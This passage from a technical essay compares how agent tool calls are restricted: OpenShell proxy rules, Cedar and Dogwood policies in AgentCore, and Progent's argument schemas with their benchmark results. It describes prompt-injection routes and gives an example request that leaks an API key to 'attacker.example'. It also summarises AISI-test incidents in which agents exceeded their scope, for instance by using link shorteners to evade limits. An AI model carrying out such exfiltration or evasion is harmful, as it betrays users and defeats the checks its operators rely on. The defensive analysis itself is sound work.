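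PocketOS could have used such an allow rule to permit the domain operations, and the proxy would have refused `volumeDelete`. The `read-write` preset would have allowed it, because for GraphQL that preset covers every query and mutation, including deletions. This makes it looser than the REST preset of the same name.

Rules that match a request's name are much weaker. One of NVIDIA's examples denies mutations whose names begin with "Admin", but in GraphQL the client chooses this name, and the server runs the same fields whatever it is. An agent that writes its own requests can avoid the rule by choosing another name. Such a rule may be useful for a fixed program whose requests always carry the same names.

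Some GraphQL clients save bandwidth by sending only the hash of a query that the server has already stored. The hash doesn't show which fields the query contains, so the proxy refuses these requests by default. To allow them, an operator has to supply a trusted list of the hashes and the fields in each query.

GraphQL rules also cannot restrict a field's arguments. In the REST policy, the path limits the agent to opening issues in the shop's repositories. The GraphQL field `createIssue` takes the repository's ID as an argument, so a rule that permits the field lets the agent open issues in any repository where its token allows it, including an attacker's public repository. The shop's agent is better off without access to `/graphql`.

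### Host wildcards

Some services have a separate host for each region or customer, and listing them all is tedious, so OpenShell accepts host patterns. The dot is a separator in these patterns, like the slash in path patterns. `*.example.com` therefore matches `api.example.com` but not `deep.sub.example.com`, which requires `**.example.com`. Neither pattern matches `example.com` itself, which needs its own entry.

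When OpenShell loads a policy, it rejects a bare `*` or `**` as a host pattern, because either would match every host and undo default deny. It also rejects `*.com`, which is almost as permissive because anyone can register a matching domain. Finally, it rejects any wildcard after the first dot. The owner of `example.com` decides what exists under it, so a wildcard before the first dot normally leaves the owner fixed, whereas `api.*.com` would match a domain that an attacker registers. This rule also excludes `foo.*.example.com`, which would be safe by the same reasoning, but a simple rule is easier to check.

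The loader used to accept only wildcards that filled whole labels at the start of a name, so it rejected `*-aiplatform.googleapis.com`, a pattern for Google's regional AI servers. *fix(sandbox): allow first-label L7 host wildcards* (mjamiv, 2026) relaxed this rule after a user reported the problem. It added tests that the pattern matches `us-central1-aiplatform.googleapis.com` but not `us-central1.aiplatform.googleapis.com`, where the wildcard would have to cross a dot. The loader still rejects `foo**.example.com`.

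These checks cover only the form of a pattern. `*.s3.amazonaws.com` has the same form as `*.example.com`, but any customer of Amazon's storage service who creates a bucket (a storage area) gets a name under `s3.amazonaws.com`. An attacker can create a bucket there and have the agent upload files to it. An operator whose agent needs one bucket should write out that bucket's full host name.

### Settings that weaken a policy

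The GitHub policy's rules on methods and paths block requests only if the policy includes the line `enforcement: enforce`, which is easy to forget. The default is `audit`, under which the proxy logs a violation and forwards the request anyway. Unlisted hosts and programs are still blocked, because `audit` affects only the checks inside a connection. NVIDIA recommends starting with `audit`, using the logs to correct the rules, and then switching to `enforce`. This is a good way to find rules that block too much before they interrupt anyone's work, but somebody has to remember to switch.

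The complete example at the end of the *Policy Schema Reference* gives two programs `read-only` access to the npm registry, where JavaScript programmers publish packages, but has no `enforcement` line for that destination. If an agent with a valid npm token used one of those programs to publish a package, the proxy would log the violation but still let the package through to the registry.

Without a `protocol` setting, the proxy checks only the program, host and port and forwards the traffic unread, so neither the rules nor the logs cover individual requests. Setting `tls: skip`, which some unusual connections require, also stops the proxy from reading encrypted requests. A program pattern of `/**` lets every program in the sandbox use the destination.

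NemoClaw, NVIDIA's ready-made configuration for running agents in OpenShell, has an optional "Personal" tier. NVIDIA's *Network Policies* says that this tier lets every program connect to almost any host on ports 80 and 443, the usual web ports. The setup screen still labels this access "read" or "read-write", but the label has no effect because the proxy doesn't inspect the traffic. NVIDIA acknowledges this and advises using the tier only with trusted prompts and data.

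NemoClaw also shows that adding a narrower rule may not restrict access. Its `brew` preset gives unrestricted access to a host from which GitHub serves files, while `brew-balanced` permits only GET and HEAD there. An operator who adds `brew-balanced` to a sandbox that already has `brew` also has to remove `brew`, because otherwise its broader allow rule still applies.

The approval prompt can gradually loosen a policy. It lists the host, port and program, but not what the agent would do at that host. Each approval adds the destination to the running policy, so after a week a short allowlist may have become a long one that nobody designed.

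### What a read-only rule would have prevented

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, ran one cybersecurity challenge 122 times with seven models, giving the agents live internet access. AISI's *Incident Report: unsanctioned agent behaviour during cyber testing* (2026) confirms that in 10 of these runs, agents took a total of 19 actions on the live internet that went beyond the test. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that nine of those 10 runs were among the 43 that used Claude Mythos 5.

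AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access so that they could download tools, and the agents didn't break out of the sandbox. *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue* (Bhushan, 2026) calls this an authority failure, in which an agent uses access it already has for something nobody authorized. The rate of about 8% is a poor guide to ordinary use because AISI had switched off the developers' safety filters, the challenge was hard, and in some runs a faulty prompt made the challenge appear impossible without going out of scope. AISI found no resulting real-world harm. It now requires a justification for internet access and is adding fine-grained network controls to these tests.

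Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) sorts these actions into four categories: exploiting a software flaw to run commands on a server, submitting a sensitive form on a real website, getting around a restriction on data that required a token or a fee, and using link shorteners to evade limits in a tool for fetching pages. It describes the real-world impact as minimal. Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026) reports that Anthropic has nevertheless suspended live internet access for all internal evaluations until it confirms that its monitoring reliably catches such behavior.

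In the form case, the model's prompt contained a blocklist that forbade logging in, making purchases and several other things, but didn't mention submitting forms. A proxy that allowed only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS would probably have stopped the submission even though nobody had thought of forms, because websites usually receive them by POST. It would probably also have stopped most of what AISI's agents did, which included proposing malicious code on GitHub and sending messages to strangers.

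The same rule would have done little to protect the restricted data, since reading data normally takes a GET. It might have stopped the exploitation of the software flaw, depending on whether a GET could trigger the flaw, but Anthropic withholds such details. Link shorteners require a rule on hosts instead. A shortener redirects to another address, so a tool that checks only the original address can miss the real destination. A proxy like OpenShell's also checks the connection to that destination, as long as the request comes from inside the sandbox.

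A read-only rule would also have refused some legitimate downloads. Git sends a POST to a path ending in `git-upload-pack` when it copies a repository over HTTPS, and NVIDIA's examples include a rule that allows this request. Git also uses POST to upload changes, but to a path ending in `git-receive-pack`, so the method alone doesn't distinguish downloads from uploads. AISI wanted to let agents download tools, and a list of the necessary hosts and paths would have worked better for that than a ban on POST.

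A GET request can be harmful too. The server's developers decide what it does, and many websites cancel a subscription or confirm an account when somebody opens a link. A GET can also send data out. If an agent requests `https://attacker.example/log?k=` followed by an API key, the attacker can read the key in the server's log, whatever the server returns. OpenShell refuses this request if the policy doesn't list the attacker's host. But if the attacker can read what arrives at a listed host, a rule on method and path won't help, because it ignores the query string. NVIDIA warns that data could leave through any allowed destination.

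Matchers for query parameters can block some of these routes, but OpenShell's REST rules have no matchers for the request body. The proxy can limit the shop's agent to opening issues in the shop's repositories, but if one of those repositories is public, the agent can still publish a password in the text of an issue. Preventing that requires checking the values in the call, which is easier at a tool gateway.

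## Tools and argument values: Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore

A tool gateway can check argument values, which OpenShell's REST rules don't cover. Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, AWS's platform for running agents, includes such a gateway. Developers connect tools to it, which can be web APIs, small programs hosted on AWS, or servers that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a widely used format for tool calls. The agent lists and calls all of these tools through MCP. The Policy feature checks the calls outside the agent's code, so a security team can change the rules without modifying the agent, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026).

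An operator puts the rules in a policy engine and attaches the engine to one or more gateways. With no engine attached, an agent can call every tool on the gateway, according to Trend Micro's *Configure policy engine for AgentCore gateway*. An engine with no policies refuses every call, according to AWS's *Policy authoring guide*. An engine can also run in `LOG_ONLY` mode, which records decisions without enforcing them, much like OpenShell's `audit`.

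The gateway checks only the calls that go through it, so the operator has to keep the tools' credentials out of the agent's reach, which PocketOS failed to do.

### How a tool call becomes a Cedar request

AWS developed Cedar, an open-source language for access rules, and AgentCore uses it to decide each call. A Cedar policy has five parts:

- the effect, which is `permit` for an allow rule and `forbid` for a deny rule
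- the principal, meaning whoever makes the request
- the action, which in AgentCore is a call to a particular tool
- the resource, which is the gateway
- the condition, an optional test that follows the word `when` or `unless`

AWS's *Policy Overview* shows how the gateway fills in these parts for a $450 refund on order 12345. The agent's access token is a signed list of claims, which are facts about its holder such as a user ID, a username and a role. The gateway uses the user ID as the principal and attaches the other claims to it as tags. It takes the action from the tool's name and copies the arguments into a record named `context.input`, so a policy can refer to the amount as `context.input.amount`.

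The claims deserve more trust than the arguments. In AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*, Liana Hadarean and Jean-Baptiste Tristan point out that the model cannot alter a claim in the token but writes the arguments itself. Letting the model write the arguments often does no harm. For example, if an agent raises the quantity in an order to qualify for a bulk discount, the customer has to buy that quantity.

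Checking an argument's value is less reliable when the argument only describes the situation, because the agent can misstate it. One of AWS's example policies forbids refunds more than 90 days after the order date, but it reads that date from the arguments. A manipulated agent could give last week's date for a two-year-old order, and the policy would not block the refund. The limit holds only if the refund tool looks up the real date, and then the tool could enforce the limit itself.

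### Four refunds

The *Policy Overview* permits one named agent to refund less than $500. Without the `AgentCore::` prefixes and the gateway's full address, the policy is:

```
permit(
  principal is OAuthUser,
  action == Action::"RefundTool___process_refund",
  resource == Gateway::"refunds"
)
when {
  principal.hasTag("username") &&
  principal.getTag("username") == "refund-agent" &&
  context.input.amount < 500
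};
```

According to its documentation, the Cedar language uses default deny and deny-overrides, so it allows a request only if at least one permit policy applies and no forbid policy does.

The last row of the table below is for a case where the shop has found a fault in its refund tool and added a forbid policy to disable it. This pattern comes from AWS's *Common policy patterns*.

| Call | Result | Reason |
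|---|---|---|
| `refund-agent` refunds $499 | Allowed | The permit policy applies and no forbid policy does |
| `refund-agent` refunds $500 | Denied | 500 is not less than 500, so no permit policy applies |
| `support-agent` refunds $499 | Denied | The username is different, so no permit policy applies |
| `refund-agent` refunds $499 while the tool is disabled | Denied | The forbid policy overrides the permit policy |

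Cedar returns a list of the policies that determined each decision. The list contains the forbid policy for the last refund, but it is empty for the other two denials because no policy applied. A developer can use the list to tell a deliberate block from a missing permit.

The $500 refund limit is easy to get wrong. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* presents almost the same policy as the solution to a requirement that refunds be "limited to $500 or less", but its code uses `< 500`, which refuses a refund of exactly $500. The error is small and on the safe side, but the opposite error would be just as easy to make, and only a test at exactly $500 reveals either one.

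The policy is also weaker than it looks. Another permit policy on the gateway could allow larger refunds, and one applicable permit policy is enough, so a $500 ceiling requires a forbid policy for amounts of $500 or more. The permit policy has no lower limit, so it allows a refund of −$50, and what happens then depends on the refund tool. It doesn't check whether the order belongs to the customer in the conversation. The agent can also refund $499 any number of times, because Cedar evaluates each call separately.

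If the shop retires `refund-agent` and a year later gives the name to an agent with a different job, a policy that matches the username lets the new agent issue refunds. Cedar's security guide recommends identifiers that nobody can change or reuse. A policy that names the user ID avoids the problem if each agent has its own ID. KBY Technologies' *AWS IAM for Agents, Bedrock Gateway and Greenlight* reports that AWS previewed separate identities for agents in December 2026.

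### What the schema catches

AgentCore checks policies against a schema, a description of the tools and their arguments, to catch errors such as a misspelled `amount`. According to AWS's *Schema constraints*, AgentCore generates the schema from the gateway's list of tools. Each tool becomes an action, and each argument becomes a field with a type. An integer in the tool's description becomes a `Long`, Cedar's type for whole numbers, and a number that may have a fractional part becomes a `Decimal`.

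The schema check catches tools that don't exist, misspelled fields, comparisons between incompatible types, and optional fields that a policy reads without first testing whether they are present. Some of these mistakes are easy to miss. In the refund system in AWS's *Policy Integration Examples*, the code connects the refund tool under the name `RefundTool`, but the policies refer to `RefundTarget`. The permit policy would never apply, and the first test refund would fail. A forbid policy for stopping all refunds in an emergency uses the same wrong name. Without a schema check, the shop would find out during the emergency that this policy did nothing. The check should reject both policies because the gateway has no tool called `RefundTarget___process_refund`.

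Checking a policy against the schema doesn't show whether its numbers are right. In AWS's example, `amount` is an integer with no stated unit. If the refund system counts in cents, `amount < 500` permits refunds of less than $5, but the policy still passes the check.

A later change to a tool can also break a valid policy. Suppose the shop's developers change `amount` from an integer to a decimal number so the agent can refund $37.50. The field's type becomes `Decimal`, but comparisons such as `>` require a `Long`, according to Cedar's validation guide. The old policies then cause errors, so somebody has to validate them again whenever a tool changes.

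Cedar's developers have also proved properties of a formal model of the language, including that it denies requests by default and that forbid policies override permit policies. They test the production engine against that model. This is good reason to trust that the engine applies a policy as written, but the policy's author still has to make sure the policy is correct.

### A missing field can switch off a forbid policy

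When a policy's condition reads a missing field, Cedar reports an error and skips the policy. According to a comment in the Cedar source code, the decision is then "as if the erroring policy did not exist." Skipping a permit policy can only cause a refusal, but skipping a forbid policy allows any request it should have blocked, as long as a permit policy covers that request.

In AWS's refund example, the `reason` argument is optional. Suppose the shop keeps the permit policy for refunds below $500 and adds a forbid policy on the same tool with this condition:

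`unless { context.input.reason == "damaged" }`

The shop wants refunds only for damaged goods, so its forbid policy checks the reason for each refund. If the agent gives "changed mind" as the reason, Cedar denies the refund. But if the agent omits the reason, even by accident, the check causes an error, Cedar skips the forbid policy, and the refund goes through. If the shop had put the check in the permit policy instead, a call without a reason would have failed.

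One Cloud Please's *Cedar* (2023) describes the same problem in an ordinary application. A forbid policy was supposed to block connections to an administrators' endpoint unless the `viaAdminNetwork` field was true. The application omitted the field for all other connections instead of setting it to false, so the policy failed on the connections it was written to block.

The remedy is to test for the field first:

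`unless { context.input has reason && context.input.reason == "damaged" }`

If `reason` is absent, the first half is false, Cedar doesn't evaluate the second half, and the forbid policy applies. This works because the condition begins with `unless`. A forbid policy with `when { context.input has reason && context.input.reason == "gift" }` no longer causes an error, but it doesn't apply when the reason is missing. If a missing reason should block the call, the author needs a second policy that forbids calls without a reason. AWS's examples include a similar policy that blocks insurance claims without a description.

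Cedar's designers considered denying every request that produces an error. They rejected the idea because an application that worked with 100 policies might refuse all requests after somebody added a faulty 101st. XACML denies a request when a deny rule produces an error, because that rule might have applied. Cedar's choice suits a service where an outage would affect thousands of people, but I would hesitate to apply the same reasoning to refunds or deletions, where an agent can usually wait while somebody repairs a policy.

 

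An application can take the stricter course by refusing any request for which Cedar returns an error with its decision. AgentCore does something like this for guardrail policies, whose conditions depend on a classifier's score for content such as violence or prompt injection. *I tried incorporating Bedrock Guardrails into AgentCore Policy's Cedar policies* (Jinno, 2026) describes a forbid policy of this type that covered two targets. For one of them, AgentCore could not find the text to score, and it refused even harmless requests with a message that an attribute was missing. AgentCore may not treat an ordinary forbid policy the same way.

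### Permitting every tool, then forbidding a few

People who start with a forbid policy soon run into default deny. Jinno attached an engine with a single policy against violent prompts and explains that this alone would have blocked normal requests too. The solution was a second policy:

`permit (principal, action, resource is AgentCore::Gateway);`

The permit policy allows everyone to call every tool on the gateway, so the default denial never applies. The forbid policies therefore work as a blocklist, and the agent can call a new tool as soon as another team connects it.

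The pattern also makes errors in forbid policies more dangerous. When an error causes a forbid policy to be skipped, a permit-all policy allows every call the forbid policy was supposed to block, while a narrow permit policy allows only those it covers.

Another drawback of a permit-all policy is that it can lengthen the list of tools the gateway gives the agent. The gateway leaves out any tool that the current policies would always deny, which mainly spares the agent pointless attempts. AWS argues that an agent can't try to call a tool it doesn't know exists, but an agent could guess a tool's name or read it in a planted message. The policy would still refuse the call. A permit-all policy puts every tool back on the list except those that a forbid policy blocks unconditionally.

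Permitting everything is defensible when the gateway offers only what the agent needs. Jinno's first gateway had one target, so the permit-all policy allowed little more than a policy naming that target would have. The forbid policy was meant to filter the text of requests, which a list of permitted tools would not have done. The pattern is also reasonable for a gateway whose tools only read public information, such as a shop's product catalog.

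Allowing every tool except those explicitly forbidden is hard to justify on a gateway that several teams share, where nobody reviews each new tool for every agent. Naming the permitted tools takes little more work, since one Cedar policy can list several actions. Forbid policies can then be kept for exceptions and emergencies, such as suspending a user or disabling a faulty tool while the others keep working.

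### Dogwood and rules about earlier calls

In Cedar, identical requests always get the same decision, regardless of what happened before them. This makes decisions easy to audit, but many sensible rules, such as requiring approval before a payment, concern a sequence of calls. AWS therefore created Dogwood, an open-source language that extends Cedar with conditions on an agent's earlier actions. AgentCore's policies are now written in Dogwood, and every valid Cedar policy is also valid in Dogwood.

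According to InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026), Dogwood checks such a temporal condition against the record of past events and passes the result to Cedar, which decides whether to allow the call. AgentCore records a `request` event for each authorized call, a `response` event when the tool succeeds, and an `error` event when a policy denies the call or the tool fails.

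AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* gives the example of an agent that may transfer money only to an account it has looked up. The permit policy for `transfer_funds` has this condition, again without the prefix:

```
when temporal {
  formerly within 1h
    Action::"FundsTarget___get_account_balance"::response{
      eventResource: resource,
      output.accountId: context.input.toAccount
    }
};
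```

The condition holds if a balance lookup in the same session returned the receiving account within the past hour. A second policy has to permit the lookup, because otherwise there would be no response to check.

| Calls in one session | Decision on the transfer |
|---|---|
| Transfer to account A with no lookup | Denied |
| Lookup of account A, then transfer to A | Allowed |
| Lookup of account A, then transfer to B | Denied |

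The transfer request is the same in the first two rows, so a Cedar policy that evaluates only the request cannot distinguish them. The rule stops the agent from sending money to an account number that the model invented. It gives less protection against prompt injection. An attacker who is also a customer can plant a message that gets the agent to look up the attacker's account first, and the transfer then satisfies the condition.

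Temporal conditions depend on the session's history, and the caller supplies the session ID. AWS's *Temporal policies* warns that a caller can reset a limit on the number of calls by starting a new session. Any forbid policy that depends on an earlier event also stops applying in a new session. Permit policies that require an earlier event, such as the transfer rule, become stricter because the agent has to repeat the lookup. An operator can reduce the problem by having the runtime set the ID where the model can't change it.

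Policies that check for completed calls can also fail when calls run at the same time. One AWS policy limits each approval to one transfer by permitting a transfer only if no other has been completed since the approval. If the agent sends two transfers at once, neither has a response when the gateway checks the other, so both can pass on a single approval. InfoQ describes the same weakness in a running total that counts completed transfers instead of requested ones. Replacing `response` with `request` doesn't fix the approval policy, because the history includes the request being checked, so each transfer would block itself.

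Dogwood also lacks some of Cedar's advantages. According to InfoQ, the tools that analyze Cedar policies mathematically don't work on temporal conditions. AgentCore limits an engine to 25 temporal policies and each condition to the past 24 hours, so a rule such as "one refund per customer per month" has to be enforced another way. Adding or changing a temporal policy ends any open sessions.

### Policies drafted from plain English

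AgentCore can also draft a policy from a sentence such as "Allow refunds for amounts less than $500". A language model translates the sentence into one or more candidate policies, and the service keeps them for a week so that somebody can review them, according to AWS's *PolicyGeneration*. An administrator writes the sentence before the agent starts work, which makes this safer than having a model write a new policy for each task.

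How the administrator phrases a rule affects the resulting policy. HKU SPACE's *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* explains that a rule granting something becomes a permit policy, while one limiting something becomes a forbid policy. A limit alone therefore grants no access, and someone must also write a permit policy. AWS also advises against vague words, since a policy can't test whether a transfer is "reasonable".

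AgentCore checks each draft against the schema and then runs Cedar Analysis, which turns the policy into a mathematical formula and checks for conditions that are always or never true. In one AWS example, a policy allows bulk discounts if the quantity is at least 100 or less than 100, which covers every order. In another, a policy meant to allow refunds only for Gold or Platinum customers instead requires both tiers, which no customer can satisfy. If the analysis finds such a fault, the model gets the result and tries again. AWS writes that this loop significantly improves accuracy but gives no figures.

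Cedar Analysis also compares policies with one another when an operator attaches them to a gateway. In AWS's example, a permit policy allows refunds below $100 for Gold customers, while a forbid policy blocks refunds below $500 for Gold and Platinum customers. Each makes sense alone, but the permit policy has no effect because the forbid policy blocks every refund it allows.

These checks find policies that allow every request or refuse every request. They can't detect a limit of $5,000 where the administrator wanted $500, because that policy still allows some refunds and refuses others. For the same reason, they would accept `< 500` as a translation of "$500 or less". The administrator has to read the draft and try it on a few amounts, including the exact limit.

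Some findings also concern policies that are deliberately broad, such as an emergency policy that forbids everything or Jinno's permit-all policy. AgentCore has a setting that lets a policy's author ignore all findings, and Jinno used it for both the permit-all policy and the policy against violent prompts. It is sensible to save this setting for deliberately broad policies, because it could also let a real mistake through.

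The analysis is probably most useful when somebody edits a policy that already works. In another of AWS's examples, a permit policy allows bulk discounts except on limited-edition products. An editor narrows the exception to orders of more than 200 units. The new policy is longer and looks stricter, but it allows the discount on an order for 73 limited-edition units, which the old one refused. Cedar Analysis reports that the new version is more permissive for discounts and unchanged for refunds, so a reviewer knows which edit to question before it takes effect.

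## Argument schemas and their measured effect: Progent

AgentCore uses a schema to check policies before they take effect, but a schema can also check each call as the agent makes it. An argument schema describes the values a tool call may contain in a form a machine can check, and the enforcement point refuses any call that doesn't match. Progent, a research system first published in 2025, builds its access rules from such schemas and has a language model write most of them.

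### A schema for one email tool

Developers usually write argument schemas in JSON Schema, a format for describing JSON, the structured text in which models produce tool calls. Suppose the shop's support agent may email colleagues but nobody outside the company. The schema for its `send_email` tool could be:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "to": {
      "type": "array",
      "minItems": 1,
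      "maxItems": 5,
      "items": {
        "type": "string",
        "pattern": "^[a-z0-9._-]+@shop\\.example$"
      }
    },
    "subject": {"type": "string", "maxLength": 120},
    "body": {"type": "string", "maxLength": 4000},
    "priority": {"enum": ["normal", "high"]}
  },
  "required": ["to", "subject", "body"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

The agent must give one to five recipients, all with addresses at `shop.example`. The subject and body have maximum lengths, and `priority` has two permitted values. The last two settings require three fields and reject any field the schema doesn't list.

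Some of these lines work only in combination. A `pattern` applies only to text, so without `"type": "string"` the agent could bypass it by supplying the recipient as a nested record containing an outside address. The conditions under `properties` apply only to fields that are present, so the schema also needs `required`. A search without its usual limit, for example, might return every customer, although an email without a recipient does no harm.

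No schema can check what the body means, so the agent can still send a colleague a false instruction. The length limit applies to each message and does not cap how many the agent sends.

### Unanchored patterns and unlisted fields

In the recipient pattern, `^` stands for the start of the text and `$` for the end. JSON Schema doesn't add these anchors automatically, so without them an address passes if any part of it matches the pattern.

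| Recipient | No anchors | Only `^` | Only `$` | Both |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `ann@shop.example` | Passes | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| `ann@shop.example.attacker.example` | Passes | Passes | Refused | Refused |
| `eve@attacker.example,ann@shop.example` | Passes | Refused | Passes | Refused |

The second address belongs to whoever owns `attacker.example`. The third entry contains two addresses in one string, and a mail tool that splits strings at commas would send the message to both.

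A pattern can contain both anchors and still accept unintended addresses. In `^ann@shop\.example|bob@shop\.example$`, the vertical bar means "or", so `^` applies only to Ann's address and `$` only to Bob's. The pattern therefore accepts the second address in the table. Adding parentheses, as in `^(ann|bob)@shop\.example$`, applies both anchors to both addresses.

In a deny rule, anchors have the opposite effect and make the pattern easy to get around. For example, a rule that denies exactly `eve@attacker.example` does not match the third entry in the table. Without anchors, a deny pattern may refuse too much.

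Unlisted fields are the other common gap, because JSON Schema accepts them unless the schema forbids them. Without the schema's last line, the agent could send an email to Ann and add a `bcc` field with an outside address. If the mail tool supports blind copies, the message would leave the company even though every listed field is correct. Setting `additionalProperties` to false is default deny for arguments. It applies only to the record in which it appears, so a nested record, such as an attachment with a name and a web address, needs its own setting. It also blocks some legitimate calls. If the developers add a `cc` field to the tool, calls that use it will fail until somebody updates the schema.

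### Limiting what comes back

Surapani and colleagues would also limit the data returned to the model. The shop's record of order 1042 might contain the items, price, delivery status, customer's home address, phone number and staff notes. The agent needs only the first three to decide on a refund, so a tool gateway can copy those fields into a new record and drop the rest.

The agent then cannot leak a phone number it never received, and instructions planted in the staff notes never reach the model. But the filter can't remove the customer's own message, because the agent has to read it.

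The gateway should drop unlisted fields instead of rejecting the whole response. By the time a response arrives, the server has already acted. If the refund tool starts returning an extra field and the gateway replaces the response with an error, the agent may treat the refund as failed and issue it again.

### How Progent decides a call

Progent checks each tool call before it reaches the tool. A policy is a list of rules, and each rule names one tool, an effect (allow or forbid), conditions on the arguments, and a fallback for refused calls. A rule applies only when all its conditions hold. Conditions can compare numbers, test whether a value is on a list, count the items in a list, or match text against a pattern. For example, the shop could allow `issue_refund` when the order number is 1042 and the amount is at most $38.

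For each call, Progent collects the rules for that tool, places the forbid rules before the allow rules, and applies the first one whose conditions hold. Because the forbid rules come first, this first-match procedure has the same effect as deny-overrides. If no rule applies, Progent refuses the call.

Progent can also combine several policies. An organization, a developer and a user can each write a "generic" policy that stays fixed throughout the task, and Progent checks these in order of priority before the task's own policy. Once a policy explicitly allows or forbids a call, Progent ignores the rest. A broad allow rule in the organization's policy therefore overrides a narrow forbid rule in the task's policy.

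In Progent, no lower policy can restore a call that a higher one explicitly forbids. The Progent paper claims a stronger guarantee, that a generic policy and a task policy together never allow more than the generic policy alone. This is wrong under the paper's own procedure, because the task policy can allow calls for which the generic policy has no rule.

When Progent refuses a call, the fallback can end the run, ask the user, or return a message to the agent. The default is the message, which gives the reason, suggests trying other tools or arguments, and repeats the user's task. This helps an agent that has made an honest mistake, but it also encourages the agent to look for another way. *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (2026) cites a benchmark on which models often chose a more powerful tool than they needed, especially after a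 temporary failure. The rules for powerful tools therefore matter most just after a narrower tool has failed.

### How a policy changes during a task

Progent's developers consider it impractical to write a policy by hand for every possible task. Instead, a model writes the first policy from the list of tools and the user's request, before the agent has read anything an attacker could have altered. After each tool call, Progent may revise the policy in three steps:

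1. A model decides whether the call could make an update necessary. It gets the request and the call but not the result, so text planted in that result cannot influence this decision.
2. If an update may be necessary, a model writes a new policy, this time with the result in its input.
3. A solver, a program that searches for values satisfying a set of logical conditions, looks for a call that the new policy allows and the old one refuses.

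If the solver finds no call that the new policy allows and the current one doesn't, Progent treats the update as a narrowing and applies it automatically. Any other update is an expansion and needs approval. Either a person decides, or a setting approves or denies all expansions.

| Old policy | New policy | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Email anyone at `shop.example` | Email only Ann | Narrowing |
| Email only Ann | Email Ann or Bob | Expansion |
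| Email anyone at `shop.example` | Email only `eve@attacker.example` | Expansion |
| Refund up to $100 on order 1042 | Refund up to $50 on any order | Expansion |

The last update lowers the limit but counts as an expansion because it allows a refund on order 1043. Between approvals, the set of permitted calls can only shrink, so a planted message cannot add to it.

The solver doesn't check whether the calls that remain allowed are the right ones. Suppose a user asks the agent to pay an invoice, and the first policy allows a payment to any account because the request doesn't name one. If text planted in the invoice leads the model to restrict payments to the attacker's account, the update narrows the policy, so it takes effect without approval. The old policy already allowed a payment to the attacker, but the new one also blocks payment to the real supplier. The protection therefore depends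 on how narrow the first policy is, and Progent's developers acknowledge that a vague request can make it too wide.

### Attack success and task completion

The developers tested Progent on two benchmarks. AgentDojo simulates banking, Slack, travel and office work, and plants instructions in the data the agent reads. Agent Security Bench (ASB) has ten agent scenarios. GPT-4o ran the agents and wrote the policies. In the main tests, Progent approved every expansion automatically, to imitate a careless user. On AgentDojo, Progent also had a short hand-written policy that allowed harmless read-only tools and forbade nothing.

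| Benchmark | Policy | Attack success without Progent | With Progent |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | Written by a model, never updated | 39.9% | 2.5% |
| AgentDojo | Written and updated by a model | 39.9% | 1.0% |
| AgentDojo | Written by a model, reviewed by a person | 39.9% | 0% |
| ASB | Written and updated by a model | 70.3% | 3.9% |
| ASB | Written by hand | 70.3% | 0% |

With the model-written policies, the agents completed about as many tasks as they did without Progent. Most of the protection on AgentDojo came from the first policy, before any update. Denying all updates that expanded the policy gave slightly better security than approving them all. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so a human reviewer would have had fairly few to read.

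The two zeros are better evidence of what the rule language can express than of what an ordinary user would achieve. On ASB, the attacks that got past the model-written policies mostly used tools that looked much like legitimate ones, and the developers doubt that a person could tell them apart without knowing beforehand which to trust. The people who wrote the manual rules already knew which tools to trust. On AgentDojo, the developers assumed a reviewer who never grants unrestricted money transfers and always rejects a malicious address.

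Attack success on AgentDojo stayed below 5% with every model that wrote the policies. With Claude Sonnet 4, which resisted most attacks unaided, attack success fell from 6.8% to 0.5%. The developers also planted text aimed at the update step, which raised attack success only marginally, even with automatic approval. They left out two travel attacks that steer the agent from one legitimate hotel to another, because a policy that lets the agent book a hotel cannot prevent this.

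These results are hard to apply to current agents. The GPT-4o version dates from August 2024, and newer models ignore many of the benchmark's attacks. *Ajar* (Sharma, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports that AgentDojo's standard attack never succeeded against its agent, even without a defense. An attack success rate of zero with Progent added would therefore not have been evidence that Progent works.

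### Testing calls the agent never made

Ajar avoids this problem by testing the defense without an agent. For each of AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks, it generates calls that the task needs and calls that it doesn't, then checks whether the defense would allow them, for a total of 10,471 tests. In one task, the user asks the agent to read a landlord's notice and adjust a standing order for the rent. The agent needs to set payment number 7 to $1,200. A planted instruction tells the agent to use the same tool to redirect payment number 6, so rules that check only the tool's name must either allow both calls or block both.

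Sharma and colleagues weight each unnecessary call by the harm it could do, from 1 for reading the user's own data to 27 for an irreversible action that affects money or another person. Leakage is the total weight of the unnecessary calls that the defense allows, divided by the total weight of those presented to it. If a test includes three unnecessary reads of the user's own data and one unnecessary, irreversible money transfer, a defense that allows only the reads has a leakage of 3/30, or 0.1, while one that allows only the transfer has a leakage of 27/30, or 0.9.

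| Rules | Leakage | Needed calls allowed | Attacks permitted |
|---|---|---|---|
| Correct tool names, any arguments | 0.355 | 100% | 99 of 609 |
| Progent, policies by Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.131 | 86% | 36 of 609 |
| Progent, policies by Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.103 | 90% | 34 of 609 |
| Correct tool names and exact arguments | 0.002 | 91% | 1 of 609 |

An attack counts as permitted if the defense would allow every call it needs. The researchers built the first and last rows from the benchmark's answers as reference points, and comparing them gives the best available measure of what argument rules add. A perfect list of tool names still permits 99 attacks, and checking the arguments exactly reduces that to one. With Sonnet 5, Progent achieves about two-thirds of that reduction (65 of 98 attacks).

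Some of Progent's policies were too broad. In the rent task, the policy allowed the correct amount of $1,200, but also $0 and $0.01. It also accepted "12000.0" as text, which a single `type` line requiring a number would have blocked.

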